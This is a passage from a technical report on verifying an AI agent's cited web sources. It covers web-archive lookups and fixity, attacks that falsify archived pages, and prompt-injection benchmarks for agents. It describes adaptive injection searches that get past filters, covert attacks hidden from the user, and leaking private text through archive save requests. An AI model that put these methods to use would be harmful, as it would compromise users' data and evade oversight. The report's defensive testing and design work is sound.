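The fourth step shows whether the page supports the sentence today. The analyst may also need to know whether it did when she cited it, but nobody can reconstruct the old text from a 64-character hash. If she saved the page along with its hash, the agent can read her copy. Otherwise, she can't prove that the page supported the sentence then unless someone else kept a copy.

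## What does a web archive add, and how far can its copies be trusted?

Web archives keep dated copies of pages, known as mementos. The largest public one is the Wayback Machine, run by the non-profit Internet Archive. It mostly collects pages with crawlers, but it also saves a page when someone asks.

If the analyst didn't save reference 14, a memento can show her agent that the address once existed and what the page contained around the time she cited it. It also gives the agent a copy that somebody else fetched to compare with the live page. This works only if the archive captured the page and returns it unaltered, and neither is certain.

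### Finding the copy nearest the citation date

*Memento* (2009) started from the problem that old copies existed but were hard to reach, because a reader had to search each archive separately. It led to the Memento protocol, a standard published as RFC 7089, which adds a date to an ordinary web request:

1. The agent's software sends the page's address to a service called a TimeGate. A line in the request, `Accept-Datetime`, gives the date it wants.
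2. The TimeGate redirects the software to the closest copy.
3. The archive returns the copy with a line called `Memento-Datetime`, which gives the actual time of capture.
4. If the software needs more copies, it requests a TimeMap, a list of every capture with its date. Some services combine the TimeMaps of several archives.

The software should always check the date in step 3, because the closest copy may be months or years away. Aturban, Klein and colleagues (2023), in *Hashes are not suitable to verify fixity of the public archived web*, asked the Wayback Machine for a church's website as of August 2008. Six weeks later, the same request led to a copy from 2009 with different content. An agent that assumed the copy matched the requested date would have judged the wrong text.

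An archive rarely has a copy of the page from the day the analyst cited it. If the copies just before and just after that day both contain her passage, the page very probably contained it in between. If only one does, the agent can report that the page changed between the dates of the two copies, but not which version she read.

Archives normally add a banner to a page and rewrite its links so that they lead to other archived pages. The agent is better off with the page as captured. According to *Collecting 16K archived web pages from 17 public web archives* (2019), most archives offer this raw version, usually by adding `id_` after the time in the address:

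`https://web.archive.org/web/20240310120000id_/https://example.org/report`

Internet Archive's *Digital archives* (2024) describes how earlier captures of a New York Times article exposed an unannounced change. The newspaper had replaced an item in a published list of reasons but left the original date on the article. An agent with only the live page would have concluded that anyone who quoted the original item had made it up.

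### Did the address ever exist?

Rao, Wong and Callison-Burch (2026), in *Detecting and Correcting Reference Hallucinations in Commercial LLMs and Deep Research Agents*, used the Wayback Machine to estimate how many addresses that language models cite are invented. They requested each cited address. If the server returned an error or didn't respond, they looked for an archived copy from any date. They counted addresses with a copy as link rot and addresses without one as invented. They left out error code 403, which usually means a site is blocking automated visitors.

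The researchers used two sets of questions. One of them, DRBench, has 100 research questions in English and Chinese. Depending on the model, between 5% and 18% of the addresses for DRBench did not resolve, and between 3% and 13% had no archive record. The paper reports 53,090 DRBench addresses from ten models, but its counts for those ten add up to only 23,269. The larger figure may include models that the researchers excluded from the analysis.

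On ExpertQA, the set of experts' questions, three models produced 168,021 addresses, and 8.2% of them did not resolve. The addresses came from the output of the models' search tools, so the failures probably reflect dead links in search services more than addresses the models invented. The paper gives no archive results for this set.

If the analyst had drafted her eighty references with one of the DRBench models, between two and eleven would have no archive record. Those models date from 2024 and 2025, and newer ones may well invent fewer addresses.

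### Is the share without a record a lower bound?

The Wayback Machine has never captured many real pages. When such a page disappears, the method used by Rao and colleagues counts its address as invented, so their share of invented addresses can't, as it stands, be the conservative lower bound they call it. They acknowledge this error in a footnote but treat it as minor.

Internet Archive's *Gone but Not Forgotten* allows a rough test. Its researchers took addresses from earlier studies of link rot, all of which had once worked, and checked how many of the dead ones had an archived copy. For the New York Times row they built their own sample:

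| Sample | Dead | Dead, with an archived copy | Dead, with no copy |
|---|---|---|---|
| 5.4 million pages from 2013–2023, from the Pew Research Center | 26% | 16% | 10% |
| The 1 million of these that represent the general web | 27% | 13% | 14% |
| 88,000 links in New York Times articles from 2013 | 40% | 38% | 2% |
| 27.3 million addresses from 1996–2021, from Old Dominion University | 65% | 65% | 0% |

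The last row is not evidence of good coverage, because the university drew its sample from the Wayback Machine itself. The New York Times row has a milder form of the same bias. Even the Pew figures overstate coverage, because Pew took many of its pages from Common Crawl, and the Wayback Machine has imported recent Common Crawl data.

In the full Pew sample, 10 of every 26 dead pages had no archived copy. Rao and colleagues would have counted all these real pages as invented.

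Their figures can be corrected for this. Let $c$ be the share of dead real pages that have an archived copy, $S$ the share of a model's addresses that are dead with a copy, and $H$ the share that are dead without one. If invented addresses never have a copy, the share $F$ that the model really invented is

$$F = H - S\,\frac{1-c}{c}$$

The table applies this with the coverage in the full Pew sample ($c = 16/26$, or 62%) and in the New York Times sample ($c = 38/40$, or 95%):

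| System | Dead, no record ($H$) | Dead, with a record ($S$) | Invented, at 62% coverage | Invented, at 95% coverage |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Gemini 2.5 Pro Deep Research | 13.3% | 5.2% | 10% | 13% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro with search | 4.8% | 1.1% | 4% | 5% |
| OpenAI Deep Research | 3.5% | 6.6% | 0% | 3% |
| Claude 3.7 Sonnet with search | 3.2% | 5.2% | 0% | 3% |

So Gemini's research agent almost certainly invented many addresses, but OpenAI's agent and Claude may have invented hardly any. For OpenAI's agent, the formula gives slightly less than zero at 62% coverage, so the archive must cover slightly more than 62% of the pages the agent cites. Search engines favour well-known pages, which archives are also more likely to capture, so the true figures probably lie between those in the last two columns.

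Other errors lower the estimate. Some sites return an ordinary page for any address, so an invented one looks live. The study also excluded every 403 response, though only 0.3% of 383 such links checked in a real browser were dead. The published range could therefore be too high or too low.

A site's owner may also have had archived copies removed. *Understanding Web Archiving Services and Their (Mis)Use on Social Media* (2018) reports that the Wayback Machine then accepted removal requests from site owners and applied their instructions for crawlers to pages it had already archived. Under that policy, someone who bought an expired domain could presumably have hidden archived copies of the previous owner's pages.

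### What happens when the model can check for itself

Rao and colleagues turned their method into urlhealth, a free tool of 83 lines of code. It returns one of four results: live, dead with an archived copy, probably invented, or unknown. They gave it to three models, which answered 435 of the ExpertQA questions and could replace any address that failed. The paper reports the share of broken addresses before and after as follows. The last two columns come from its detailed breakdown of the results with the tool:

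| Model | Broken before | Broken after | Dead or probably invented, in the breakdown | Unknown, in the breakdown |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.1 | 16.0% | 0.6% | 2.4% | 19.7% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 6.1% | 0.1% | 0.7% | 10.3% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.5 | 4.9% | 0.8% | 0.5% | 20.2% |

The paper's main result is that all three models ended below 1%. Its breakdown doesn't quite match that result, and the paper doesn't explain the difference, but the improvement is large either way. The unknown results are mostly harmless. The researchers opened 600 such addresses from the ordinary ExpertQA answers in a real browser and found that 11% were dead, while most of the others led to a paywall or a block on automated visitors.

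A smaller model, GPT-5 nano, called the tool but often kept proposing addresses that the tool had already rejected, in some cases for up to 14 rounds. As with checksums, it would be safer for ordinary software to remove the rejected addresses.

The experiment also didn't test whether the replacement pages supported the models' claims. A model that has to provide a working address could pass the tool's check with a live but irrelevant page.

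### A live address can still be hostile

urlhealth checks only whether an address works, so it counts a page full of planted instructions as live. It also counts an invented address as live if a stranger has since registered it. This is the most dangerous kind of invented address, and urlhealth never looks it up in the archive because it searches there only after a "not found" error.

A web archive can be used for the same date check as a search index. The software also looks up live addresses, and flags any that have no archived copy or were first archived after the model drafted the reference list. A copy alone doesn't show that an address is safe, because a stranger who registers the address can ask the archive to save it the same day.

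This check would raise many false alarms. In the Pew sample, 74% of the pages were live and 18% were live but unarchived, so about a quarter of the live pages had no archived copy. At that rate, about 19 of the analyst's eighty references would have no record even if all were genuine. Her references are probably better archived than a broad sample of the web, but she would still have to check some pages by hand.

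### Does an archive return the same page twice?

In 2018, an American television presenter claimed that somebody had fabricated old posts on her blog, perhaps in the Wayback Machine's copies. The Internet Archive denied that anyone had hacked its archived pages. Aturban, Alam and colleagues (2019), in *Archive Assisted Archival Fixity Verification Framework*, use the case to argue for independent evidence that an archived page has not changed since its capture, a property called fixity. An archive's checksums of its own copies are not independent evidence, and neither are a website's checksums of its own pages.

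Their framework stores the evidence elsewhere. Software downloads the raw HTML of a memento, computes its checksums and writes them to a file called a manifest. It publishes the manifest at an address that contains the manifest's own hash, then submits it to several archives. To check the memento later, the software recomputes the checksums and compares them with those in the archived manifests. It ignores any manifest stored in the same archive as the memento, so an attacker would have to alter records in several independent archives.

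The researchers tried this on 1,000 mementos from the Wayback Machine, and all of them passed. Checking a memento took 6.65 seconds on average, or 1.49 seconds when they combined 100 manifests in one file. A manifest can't reveal tampering that happened after the page was captured but before the manifest was made.

The 2023 study by Aturban and colleagues reached a much less encouraging result. They downloaded 16,627 mementos from 17 archives 39 times over about 14 months. Each time, they computed a single hash for the whole page, including its images, style sheets and scripts:

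| Result over 39 downloads | All 17 archives | Wayback Machine |
|---|---|---|
| Same hash every time | 11.5% | 7.6% |
| At least two different hashes | 88.5% | 92.4% |
| A different hash every time | 16.1% | 18.4% |

About 40% of the mementos (archived copies of web pages) had already changed at the second download. Some archived pages contained a script that chose a picture at random. In other cases, a request for a missing image made the archive fetch it from the live web, so viewing the page altered it. One archive used a service that disguised email addresses differently on each visit.

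The study sorted the changes by type and traced many of them to ordinary causes like these. Even a stable hash doesn't show that an archive's copies are good. WebCite had the highest share of unchanging hashes, but it stored few scripts and therefore reproduced many pages badly.

The 2019 result is more relevant to a reader agent, because the agent needs the page's text but not its pictures. The 2023 study shows that raw HTML isn't completely stable either, and the 2019 test covered only one archive. Still, a hash of the raw HTML seems usable as a check on an archived article. A hash of the whole page would raise so many false alarms that the analyst would soon ignore them.

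Mementos can move. According to *Where Did the Web Archive Go?* (2021), all the sampled copies from some archives became unavailable during the same 14 months. One collection moved twice, each time to a new domain. An analyst who cites a memento should also record the original address and the capture time, so that software can search for the copy elsewhere.

### Changing what an archived page shows

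An attacker may be able to change what a reader sees without touching the stored copy. Lerner, Kohno and Roesner, in *Rewriting History*, demonstrated this on the Wayback Machine in 2017. In one example that University of Washington's *Rewriting History* (2017) describes, they temporarily made a snapshot from 2011 show content from 2017. Aturban and colleagues summarise the weaknesses they found:

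- **Archive escape.** A script on the archived page builds an address while it runs, so the archive doesn't rewrite it. The browser then loads that file from the live web, and whoever now owns its domain decides what the file contains.
- **Same-origin escape.** On the live web, browsers stop an embedded frame, such as an advertisement, from altering the page around it if the two come from different sites. In an archive, both come from the archive's own domain, so this protection disappears.
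- **Anachronism injection.** The archive never captured one of the page's files. An attacker who controls the file's original address publishes a malicious version there and asks the archive to save it, and the archive then inserts it into the old page.

The Internet Archive responded by adding a Content-Security-Policy, which tells the browser to load files only from listed domains. This blocks many archive escapes, but Aturban and colleagues report that some ways of loading live content still work. A list of domains alone also does little against the other two attacks, because the malicious file comes from the archive's own domain.

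The problem persisted in 2025, when Robin Kirchner, Nick Nikiforakis and colleagues described two new kinds of attacker in *The Power to Never Be Wrong* and tested eight well-known archives against them. Martin Johns, a professor at Kirchner's university, TU Braunschweig, says in its press release (2025) that the weaknesses effectively let an attacker falsify archived content after the fact.

An agent can avoid most of these attacks by reading the raw HTML without running scripts, since they mostly work by changing what a browser loads or runs. It would then miss any text that a script adds to the page. The search services that Chen and colleagues tested already ignore such text on live pages, so for many agents this would be no new loss.

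### Sites that treat the archive's crawler differently

One of the new attackers in the 2025 paper is a publisher who recognises an archive's crawler. Elbsides' *'We Have Always Been at War With Eastasia'* (2026), a summary of a conference talk on such attacks, explains that this publisher can hide from the archive or selectively deceive it. An archived copy is therefore less valuable as an independent view of a page.

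Suppose the agent's software asks an archive to save reference 14 today and compares that copy with the page the agent received:

| Served to the agent | Served to the archive | Served to people | What the comparison shows |
|---|---|---|---|
| Hostile page | Ordinary page | Ordinary page | A mismatch, which exposes the cloaking |
| Hostile page | Hostile page | Ordinary page | A match, so the cloaking goes unnoticed |
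| Ordinary page | Altered page | Ordinary page | A mismatch, though the agent's copy is the honest one |

An attacker who wants to escape notice therefore has to serve the archive the same hostile page it serves agents, which leaves public evidence of the attack. Many attackers would presumably rather show the archive the clean version, and then comparing the archived copy with the page the agent received reveals the difference. The case in the third row is more dangerous for an agent that relies on the archive instead of the live page. A publisher could use the same method to give the archive a more flattering version of an old statement.

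### Hostile text under a trusted name

Khodayari and colleagues found that archives also preserve planted instructions. An agent therefore needs the same protection when it reads an archived copy as when it reads a live page, including a label that marks the content as untrusted.

If the analyst's URL gate permits `web.archive.org`, it allows every page the archive has captured, including any that an attacker asked it to save yesterday. The gate should also check the original address inside the memento's address.

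An attacker could also use the archive to steal data. When someone asks the Wayback Machine to save a page, the archive requests that address from the live site. An agent that can submit any address could therefore send private text to an attacker by putting it in the address, without contacting the attacker's site itself. The remedy is to have ordinary software, rather than the agent, submit only the addresses in the reference list.

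### Publishers that block the archive

The Wayback Machine is losing access to some of the most-cited sources. In June 2026, the Inquirer article *AI scraping is unintentionally hurting the Wayback Machine* (2026) reported that several major publishers had started to block it, but gave no number. The publishers want to stop AI companies from using their work without permission, and controls that keep out AI crawlers can also keep out archives. Open Access Tracking Project's *Wayback Machine Director* (2026) quotes the archive's director, Mark Graham, who calls it "collateral damage" in that conflict.

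The New York Times is among the publishers that block it, according to the same page. Captures like those that exposed the newspaper's unannounced edit in 2024 would therefore be hard to obtain for an article it publishes now. Graham also says that a senior researcher at the newspaper thanked him for the Wayback Machine because it held material that staff couldn't find in their own archives.

When a site blocks the archive, a missing record is weaker evidence that a cited address was invented. A real article from that site will have no archived copy, and if the publisher later removes it, urlhealth will report the address as probably invented. This error will become more common as more sites block the archive, and it will mostly affect recent news. Software could reduce it by keeping a list of sites known to block archives and reporting "unknown" for their addresses.

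The analyst can still save a blocked article herself when she cites it. To prove later that she hasn't altered her copy, she could publish its checksum on her own page and ask several archives to save that page, as in the 2019 framework. The archived checksum would show that her file existed in that form when the archives saved the page, but not that the newspaper had published it. For that, she would need a signature from the publisher or a second person who saved the same text.

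## What do existing attack sets measure?

Most of the success rates in the earlier sections come from a few public attack sets. An attack set gives an agent tasks in a simulated inbox, bank or website, plants attacks in the material the agent reads, and counts the results. The main sets are good for measuring whether a planted instruction leads to a harmful action. They reveal little about how much data an agent leaks, and none of their tasks include a page that has changed since it was cited.

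### Five measures

Suppose a tester runs an agent $n$ times with an attack present and $m$ times without one. Five measures describe the results:

| Measure | Formula | Meaning of the symbols |
|---|---|---|
| Attack success rate | $\frac{1}{n}\sum s_i$ | $s_i$ is 1 if the attacker reaches the goal in attacked run $i$, otherwise 0 |
| Utility without attack | $\frac{1}{m}\sum v_j$ | $v_j$ is 1 if the agent completes the user's task in clean run $j$, otherwise 0 |
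| Utility under attack | $\frac{1}{n}\sum u_i$ | $u_i$ is 1 if the agent completes the user's task in attacked run $i$, otherwise 0 |
| False-block rate | $B / H$ | $H$ is the number of harmless calls the agent proposes, and $B$ is how many of them the defence blocks |
| Data leaked per session | $\frac{1}{n}\sum b_i$ | $b_i$ is the number of bits of a planted secret that the attacker can recover from run $i$ |

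Suppose every successful attack steals a 128-bit key. The following invented figures show why the attack success rate is misleading by itself:

| Invented defence | Attack success | Utility without attack | Utility under attack | False blocks | Data leaked |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | 40% | 80% | 65% | 0% | 51 bits |
| Blocks every call | 0% | 0% | 0% | 100% | 0 bits |
| Blocks selectively | 2% | 74% | 72% | 6% | 2.6 bits |

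A tester needs at least one measure of useful work, because a defence that blocks every call gets the best scores for both attack success and leaked data.

In *AgentDyn*, Li, Wen and colleagues (2026) found that CaMeL completed none of the AgentDyn tasks and that no attack succeeded against it. They call this kind of failure over-defence.

They report attack success and both kinds of utility, but not the false-block rate. Lost utility is a rough substitute because an agent can fail a task for reasons unrelated to the defence, or find another way to finish after a wrongly blocked call. To measure false blocks directly, a tester has to log every blocked call and decide whether it was harmless. Measuring leaked data likewise requires a log of outgoing requests.

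### Simulated offices, shops and websites

AgentDojo dates from 2024, and researchers have used it to test many of the defences described earlier. It pairs each user task with every attacker goal in the same simulated setting. This produces 949 attack cases in the version that Lee, Kim and Lee (2026) used in *Will the User Ever Know?* AgentDyn, from February 2026, uses the same method:

| Set and setting | User tasks | Attacker goals | Attack cases |
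|---|---|---|---|
| AgentDojo: banking | 16 | 9 | 144 |
| AgentDojo: team chat | 21 | 5 | 105 |
| AgentDojo: travel | 20 | 7 | 140 |
| AgentDojo: office work | 40 | 14 | 560 |
| AgentDyn: shopping | 20 | 9 | 180 |
| AgentDyn: software projects on GitHub | 20 | 9 | 180 |
| AgentDyn: daily life | 20 | 10 | 200 |

The attack sets contain less evidence than their large case counts suggest. AgentDyn's 560 cases come from 60 tasks and 28 goals, so one unusually easy task or goal affects many results.

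In both sets, the agent's tool calls change the simulated environment, for example by making a payment. Software then checks whether the agent completed the user's task and whether it achieved the attacker's goal, so no person or language model has to judge the outcome.

AgentDyn's tasks are longer than AgentDojo's, averaging 7.1 steps rather than 3.5, and they offer the agent about 33 tools rather than 20. Li and colleagues found that only 6 of AgentDojo's 97 tasks require the agent to change its plan after reading something. A defence that fixes the plan at the start therefore loses little performance on AgentDojo, even if it would be a nuisance in practice.

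Every AgentDyn task requires such a change and contains at least one helpful third-party instruction, such as a request to enter a code the bank has emailed. A defence that removes all instructions from outside text will fail these tasks. A reference checker faces the same difficulty when a page carries a notice that a paper has moved or that a corrected version is available.

The two sets also place attacks in different parts of a web page. AgentDojo represents a page as a few words of plain text and puts the attack in the main text. AgentDyn uses realistic HTML and puts attacks only in advertisements, because Li and colleagues think it unreasonable to assume that a site's owner would plant instructions on their own page.

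That assumption is sensible for a shop but not for an agent that opens cited sources, because site operators placed most of the instructions that Khodayari and colleagues found. AgentDojo's crude pages are closer to this case than AgentDyn's realistic ones. A defence that distrusts only advertisements and comments could do well on AgentDyn and fail against a hostile publisher.

AgentDyn also tells agents not to ask the user for confirmation, because agents that stopped to ask left many tasks unfinished. This makes the test easy to automate, but the test can't measure the effectiveness of defences that rely on a person to approve doubtful calls.

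### Have recent models outgrown these sets?

Both sets come with the same standard attack, a fixed template that presents the attacker's goal as an important message. It rarely succeeds against several recent models, even without any defence. *AutoDojo* (Ma, Li and colleagues, 2026) reports that it succeeded in 0.3% of AgentDojo cases on Claude Haiku 4.5. On AgentDyn, Li and colleagues measured success rates of 0.4% on GPT-5-mini, 0.9% on Claude Sonnet 4.5 and 5.0% on GPT-5.1.

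The standard attack is now of little use for testing defences on such models, because if one attack in 300 succeeds without a defence, almost any defence will appear to work. Li and colleagues suspect that developers trained newer models on this widely known template. If so, a low success rate may reflect only training on that template.

The attack still works on some models. Lee and colleagues found that it succeeded in 41.8% of AgentDojo cases on Gemini 2.5 Flash. Calling the attack outdated for particular models is therefore more accurate than calling the whole set saturated.

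The user tasks are also becoming easier for models, though more slowly. DeepSeek-v4-Pro completed 89.5% of the tasks in three of AgentDojo's four settings. The best models in the AgentDyn paper, Claude Sonnet 4.5 and Kimi-K2.5, each completed 43 of its 60 tasks. None of these papers tests a current leading model. Such a model would presumably complete more.

InjecAgent and ASB, two other commonly used sets, are simpler still. Each task takes one step and offers the agent two or three tools, so neither set can measure what happens when an agent reads a hostile page early in a long job.

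### Fixed attacks and attacks that adapt

Replaying a fixed attack measures how a defence $D$ copes with one text, $x_0$. A real attacker can choose the most effective text from the set $X$ of everything they could write:

$$\text{ASR}(D, x_0) \le \max_{x \in X} \text{ASR}(D, x)$$

The two sides can differ greatly if, for example, a filter has learned the standard template's typical phrases but misses the same request when it is worded differently. Nobody can try every text in $X$, so an adaptive search also gives only a lower limit on what an attacker could achieve.

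AutoDojo, which supplied the adaptive test of ROPE, automates this search for the tasks in AgentDojo and AgentDyn. It works as follows:

1. Software tries some known attacks on the defended agent and ranks them by how often they succeed.
2. A language model examines the ranking and suggests why some attacks worked better than others.
3. The model writes a new attack based on that diagnosis.
4. Software puts the new text in the same place, runs the agent again and adds the result to the ranking.

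The search repeats steps 2 to 4 six times, then returns the best new text. It has no information about which defence is in use, and its only feedback is how many times each attack succeeded. The same text also has to work on several different user requests. This is realistic for a cited source, because a hostile publisher doesn't know what users have asked each visiting agent to do.

With an agent running GPT-4o-mini, the fixed attack never got past the filter PIGuard on AgentDojo, but AutoDojo's attacks succeeded in 28.0% of cases. AutoDojo's success rate reached 26.0% after two rounds and only 30.8% after twelve.

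More information can weaken the search. When Ma and colleagues told the attacking model why each attempt had failed and how PIGuard had scored it, the success rate fell to 23.4%. The model concentrated on getting past the filter and wrote texts that influenced the agent less.

The search method matters even more. Against another filter, DataFilter, AutoDojo succeeded 33.4% of the time, while four earlier adaptive methods given the same number of trial runs succeeded at most 5.7% of the time. A developer who tested DataFilter with only the earlier methods would have seriously underestimated the risk, and a stronger search might show that AutoDojo's figures underestimate it too. The human attackers and 800-attempt searches of Nasr and colleagues are a harder test, but they cost more and are difficult to repeat exactly.

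AutoDojo sometimes does worse than the fixed attack, especially against weak defences. This happens because its final text must differ from every attack it started with, even if one of those was better. A tester should therefore run both and report the higher success rate.

AutoDojo uses 389 AgentDojo cases, leaving out the office tasks, where agents completed neither the user's task nor the attacker's in 52.9% of cases. The newest models it targets include GPT-5.4-mini and DeepSeek-v4-Pro. On DeepSeek-v4-Pro with PIGuard, its search raised attack success from zero to 8.2%, so the increase isn't limited to old models.

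Chaowei Xiao, Ning Zhang and Yevgeniy Vorobeychik co-wrote AgentDyn, AutoDojo and the ROPE paper, and ROPE combines strong security with moderate utility losses on both sets. This doesn't look like simple favouritism, because Xiao and Zhang also helped create PIGuard and DRIFT, which lose far more utility. Results from an unconnected group would still be more convincing.

### How much does the user leave to the page?

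An average success rate also depends on how precisely the user tasks are worded. Ma and colleagues sorted AgentDojo's tasks into three groups and measured the fixed attack on undefended GPT-4o-mini:

| What the user's request specifies | User tasks | Attack cases | Attack success |
|---|---|---|---|
| The action and all its details | 17 | 127 | 43.3% |
| The action, with some details left to outside content | 36 | 238 | 63.9% |
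| Nothing beyond following outside content, such as a to-do list | 4 | 24 | 87.5% |

When the user has asked the agent to follow a page, an attack doesn't need to look like an instruction, because ordinary-looking data may be enough to change what the agent does. Filters that search for instructions then have little to detect.

The last row comes from only four tasks, so 87.5% is a rough figure. The pattern appeared in AgentDyn's shopping and GitHub tasks but not in its daily-life tasks, apparently because the agent followed similar steps in those whatever the wording.

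The analyst's safest request gives the agent eighty addresses and a fixed set of verdicts. Asking it to write to the contact named on each page lets the page determine the recipient, and asking it to follow each journal's correction procedure lets strangers decide what action it takes. Only 24 of the 389 cases resemble this last request, so a good average score on AgentDojo is weak evidence of how safe it would be.

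### Attacks that leave the user's task intact

An agent can complete both the user's task and the attacker's goal in the same run. Utility under attack still counts that run as a success. Publishing only separate averages for utility and attack success can hide how often this happens.

Let $A$ be the attack success rate and $U$ the utility under attack. The share $G$ of runs in which the agent completes the user's task and the attack fails lies between these limits:

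$$\max(0,\, U - A) \le G \le \min(U,\, 1 - A)$$

On AgentDyn, undefended GPT-4o had a utility under attack of 55.5% and an attack success rate of 37.8%. The share of runs that were both useful and safe could therefore be anywhere from 17.7% to 55.5%. A tester can remove this uncertainty by counting the good runs directly:

$$G = \frac{1}{n}\sum u_i(1-s_i)$$

Lee and colleagues examine a related problem, which is whether the user can tell from the agent's answer that an attack succeeded. They divide successful attacks into two groups. An overt success leaves some sign in the final answer, such as a mention of the attacker's payment. A covert success leaves none. If $a_i$ is 1 when the answer reveals the attack and 0 when it doesn't, then

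$$\text{covert rate} = \frac{1}{n}\sum s_i(1-a_i) \qquad \text{overt rate} = \frac{1}{n}\sum s_i a_i$$

The two rates add up to the ordinary attack success rate. Software can't easily recognise every way of mentioning an attack, so GPT-4o classifies each final answer by whether it reveals one. Lee and colleagues found that its classifications agreed well with those of people and another model, but people didn't check every combination of attack and defence.

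Two attacks with almost the same success rate can differ greatly in how often they stay hidden. On Llama-3.3-70B, an existing attack succeeded in 32.1% of AgentDojo's 949 cases but stayed hidden in only 2.6%. An attack that Lee and colleagues designed to stay hidden succeeded in 32.5% and stayed hidden in 23.8%.

Lee and colleagues also looked at 2,087 successful runs of existing attacks. In 67.7% of the covert cases, the agent went back to the user's task after carrying out the attacker's. In 70.9% of the overt cases, it stopped after the attacker's task and reported what it had done.

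If the analyst's agent secretly emailed her draft to a stranger and then finished checking her references, she would receive a complete table and have no obvious reason for suspicion. An overt attack would alert her, but only after the email had been sent. The log of tool calls would show both attacks, so a tester should use the log to judge security and the answer only to judge what the user could notice.

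### Longer attacks and attacks in a browser

AgentLAB, another 2026 set, contains long-horizon attacks, which develop over many steps. To test ROPE, Ma and colleagues spread attacks from AgentLAB over several items, so a detector that examines each item separately might find nothing suspicious.

An attacker who controlled several of the analyst's cited pages could try something similar. AgentLAB is therefore useful for testing whether provenance labels and tool gates still work when no single page contains the whole attack. The high success rate in the ROPE test was measured on GPT-4o-mini, an old model, so it doesn't show whether such attacks still work on current models.

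WASP, from 2025, tests browsing agents against instructions on hostile web pages, according to *MalURLBench* (Kong, Wu and colleagues, 2026). It suits tests of defences that mark or remove page content and of gates that control what an agent may click. But the test by Villa and colleagues showed that WASP can't distinguish good defences from bad ones on an agent that already resists nearly all its attacks.

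AgentDAM comes closer to measuring privacy. Its 246 tasks contain sensitive information and test whether a web agent uses only the information each task needs. An agent can fail by sharing too much on an ordinary website, without an attacker, so the results don't measure how much an attacker can extract.

New attack sets continue to appear. *MetaPI* (2026) builds injection tests from existing agent benchmarks, and *On Task, Off Track* (2026) is a benchmark for "near-target prompt injection".

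### Addresses made to look trustworthy

MalURLBench tests the decision that comes before an agent reads a page. Kong and colleagues collected addresses of real malicious websites from public blocklists, in seven categories such as phishing and fraud. They combined these with disguises for ten everyday situations, including tracking a parcel and looking for a job. The attacker can't change the registered domain name but can add reassuring words before or after it, as in these harmless examples:

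`official-parcel-tracking.attacker.example`

`attacker.example/official-parcel-tracking`

The main test used 3,150 different addresses, about 5% of the full set of 61,845 disguised addresses. For each situation, the researchers combined 15 disguises with 21 websites and asked each model about every combination five times, which makes 1,575 trials per model.

An attack succeeds if the model's answer accepts the address. The agent doesn't open the page in the main test, so the result measures misplaced trust rather than harm. In a separate demonstration, a browsing agent opened three of the websites after the researchers had checked that the sites contained only advertisements.

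The overall acceptance rates for the 12 models ranged from 32.9% to 99.9%, even though the agent had instructions to look out for attacks. These figures are less alarming than they seem, partly because the text around each address recommended it, for instance as the official page for tracking a parcel. Acceptance may therefore have depended more on the recommendation than on the disguise.

The researchers also improved the disguises that worked poorly on a particular model. Averaging their published scores for GPT-3.5-Turbo gives an acceptance rate of about 14% before these changes and 33% after. The higher figure is a reasonable estimate of what a persistent attacker could achieve, but not of how often the model would accept an ordinary malicious link. None of the models is newer than 2025, so we can't tell from these results whether current models have improved.

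MalURLBench's scoring has the same weakness as the invented table above. It counts only malicious addresses, so a model that refused every address would get a perfect score. Anyone using it to test a URL gate should add a similar number of harmless addresses and report how many the gate refuses. For a reference checker, the harmless addresses should include unfamiliar journals and long links to library databases, which a cautious model might reject.

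*Web Fraud Attacks Against LLM-Driven Multi-Agent Systems* (Kong, Peng and colleagues, 2025), an earlier study by some of the same researchers, tested 11 kinds of deceptive web address on groups of cooperating agents. One agent recommended the address and another judged it. In one set-up without added defences, the judging agent accepted 50.9% of the addresses. The best of three existing defences lowered this only to 47.2%, and the other two raised it above 80%.

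Those defences were not designed for deceptive addresses. Each combination had only ten trials, so the individual rates are rough. The study still shows the risk of relying on a language model alone to judge whether an address is safe. The reassuring words would not affect a correctly written domain list. Neither study tests whether an agent leaks private data through an address.

### Changed pages and private addresses

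The table compares the sets whose construction bears most directly on reading web pages:

| Set | Defences it can test | Does the page come from a live address? | Can the page change between citation and reading? | Does it measure data leaked through an address? |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| AgentDojo | Marking text, provenance labels and tool gates | No, it supplies simulated text | No | No, it scores whether the attacker reached the goal |
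| AgentDyn | The same, including their effect on tasks that need replanning | No, it supplies simulated HTML | No, although some pages react to what the agent does | No, it uses the same kind of score |
| AutoDojo | The same, against attacks that adapt | No, it uses the pages of AgentDojo and AgentDyn | No | No, it uses the same kind of score |
| MalURLBench | A model or filter that judges addresses | The addresses are real, but the main test opens no pages | No | No, the added words are meant to persuade the model |

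Agents in AgentDojo and AgentDyn have web tools, so an attacker's goal could include sending data through a URL, but the score would still be a yes or no. If a defence reduced a leak from a whole document to a four-digit PIN, it might get full credit if the attacker's goal was to steal the document and no credit if the goal was to steal the PIN.

The descriptions of these four sets don't mention checksums or archived copies, though other sets may include them. A high score on any of the four is not evidence that an agent would notice a rewritten page, an expired domain with a new owner, or an archived copy that differs from the live page.

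## How could all these defences be tested on cited sources?

A test of all four defences needs pages that change after someone cites them, and the main attack sets have none. The following design is a proposal, and its predictions are untested. An agent does the analyst's job and is given a list of references, the sentence that cites each one, a private draft and an email tool. For each reference, the agent returns one of four verdicts: "supports", "partly supports", "does not support" or "unable to verify".

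### One order for every check

Ordinary software takes each reference through six steps:

| Step | What the software does | If it can't complete the step |
|---|---|---|
| 1. Address check | Compares the citation date with the dates when someone registered the domain and when a crawler first recorded the address, and holds back anything newer than the citation | Holds the address back and lists it for the analyst |
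| 2. Fetch | Downloads the page without running its scripts | Tries again later, then goes to step 4 |
| 3. Hash comparison | Compares the page's readable text with the recorded hash, and skips step 4 if they match | Goes to step 4 |
| 4. Archive lookup | Looks for the cited passage in a copy from around the citation date | Limits the verdict to the current page, or returns "unable to verify" if there is no usable page |
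| 5. Provenance label | Marks the text as untrusted, and records which copy it is and how the checks went | Treats the text as untrusted anyway |
| 6. Tool check | Compares each call the agent proposes with the policy for the task | Blocks the call |

Step 1 also applies to any further address the agent asks to open. Step 5 marks the text as untrusted even when the hash matches, because a page that was already hostile when its hash was recorded will still match.

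Some systems allow requests by default when they can't check them, instead of blocking them. *What Gets Measured Gets Managed* describes software that checks a website's outgoing requests in the visitor's browser. If the software repeatedly fails to reach its server, it stops checking and lets every request through. That suits a shop that has to stay online, but an attacker who can cut off the server can switch off the defence. A reference checker can tolerate delays, so it can block requests until the checks work again.

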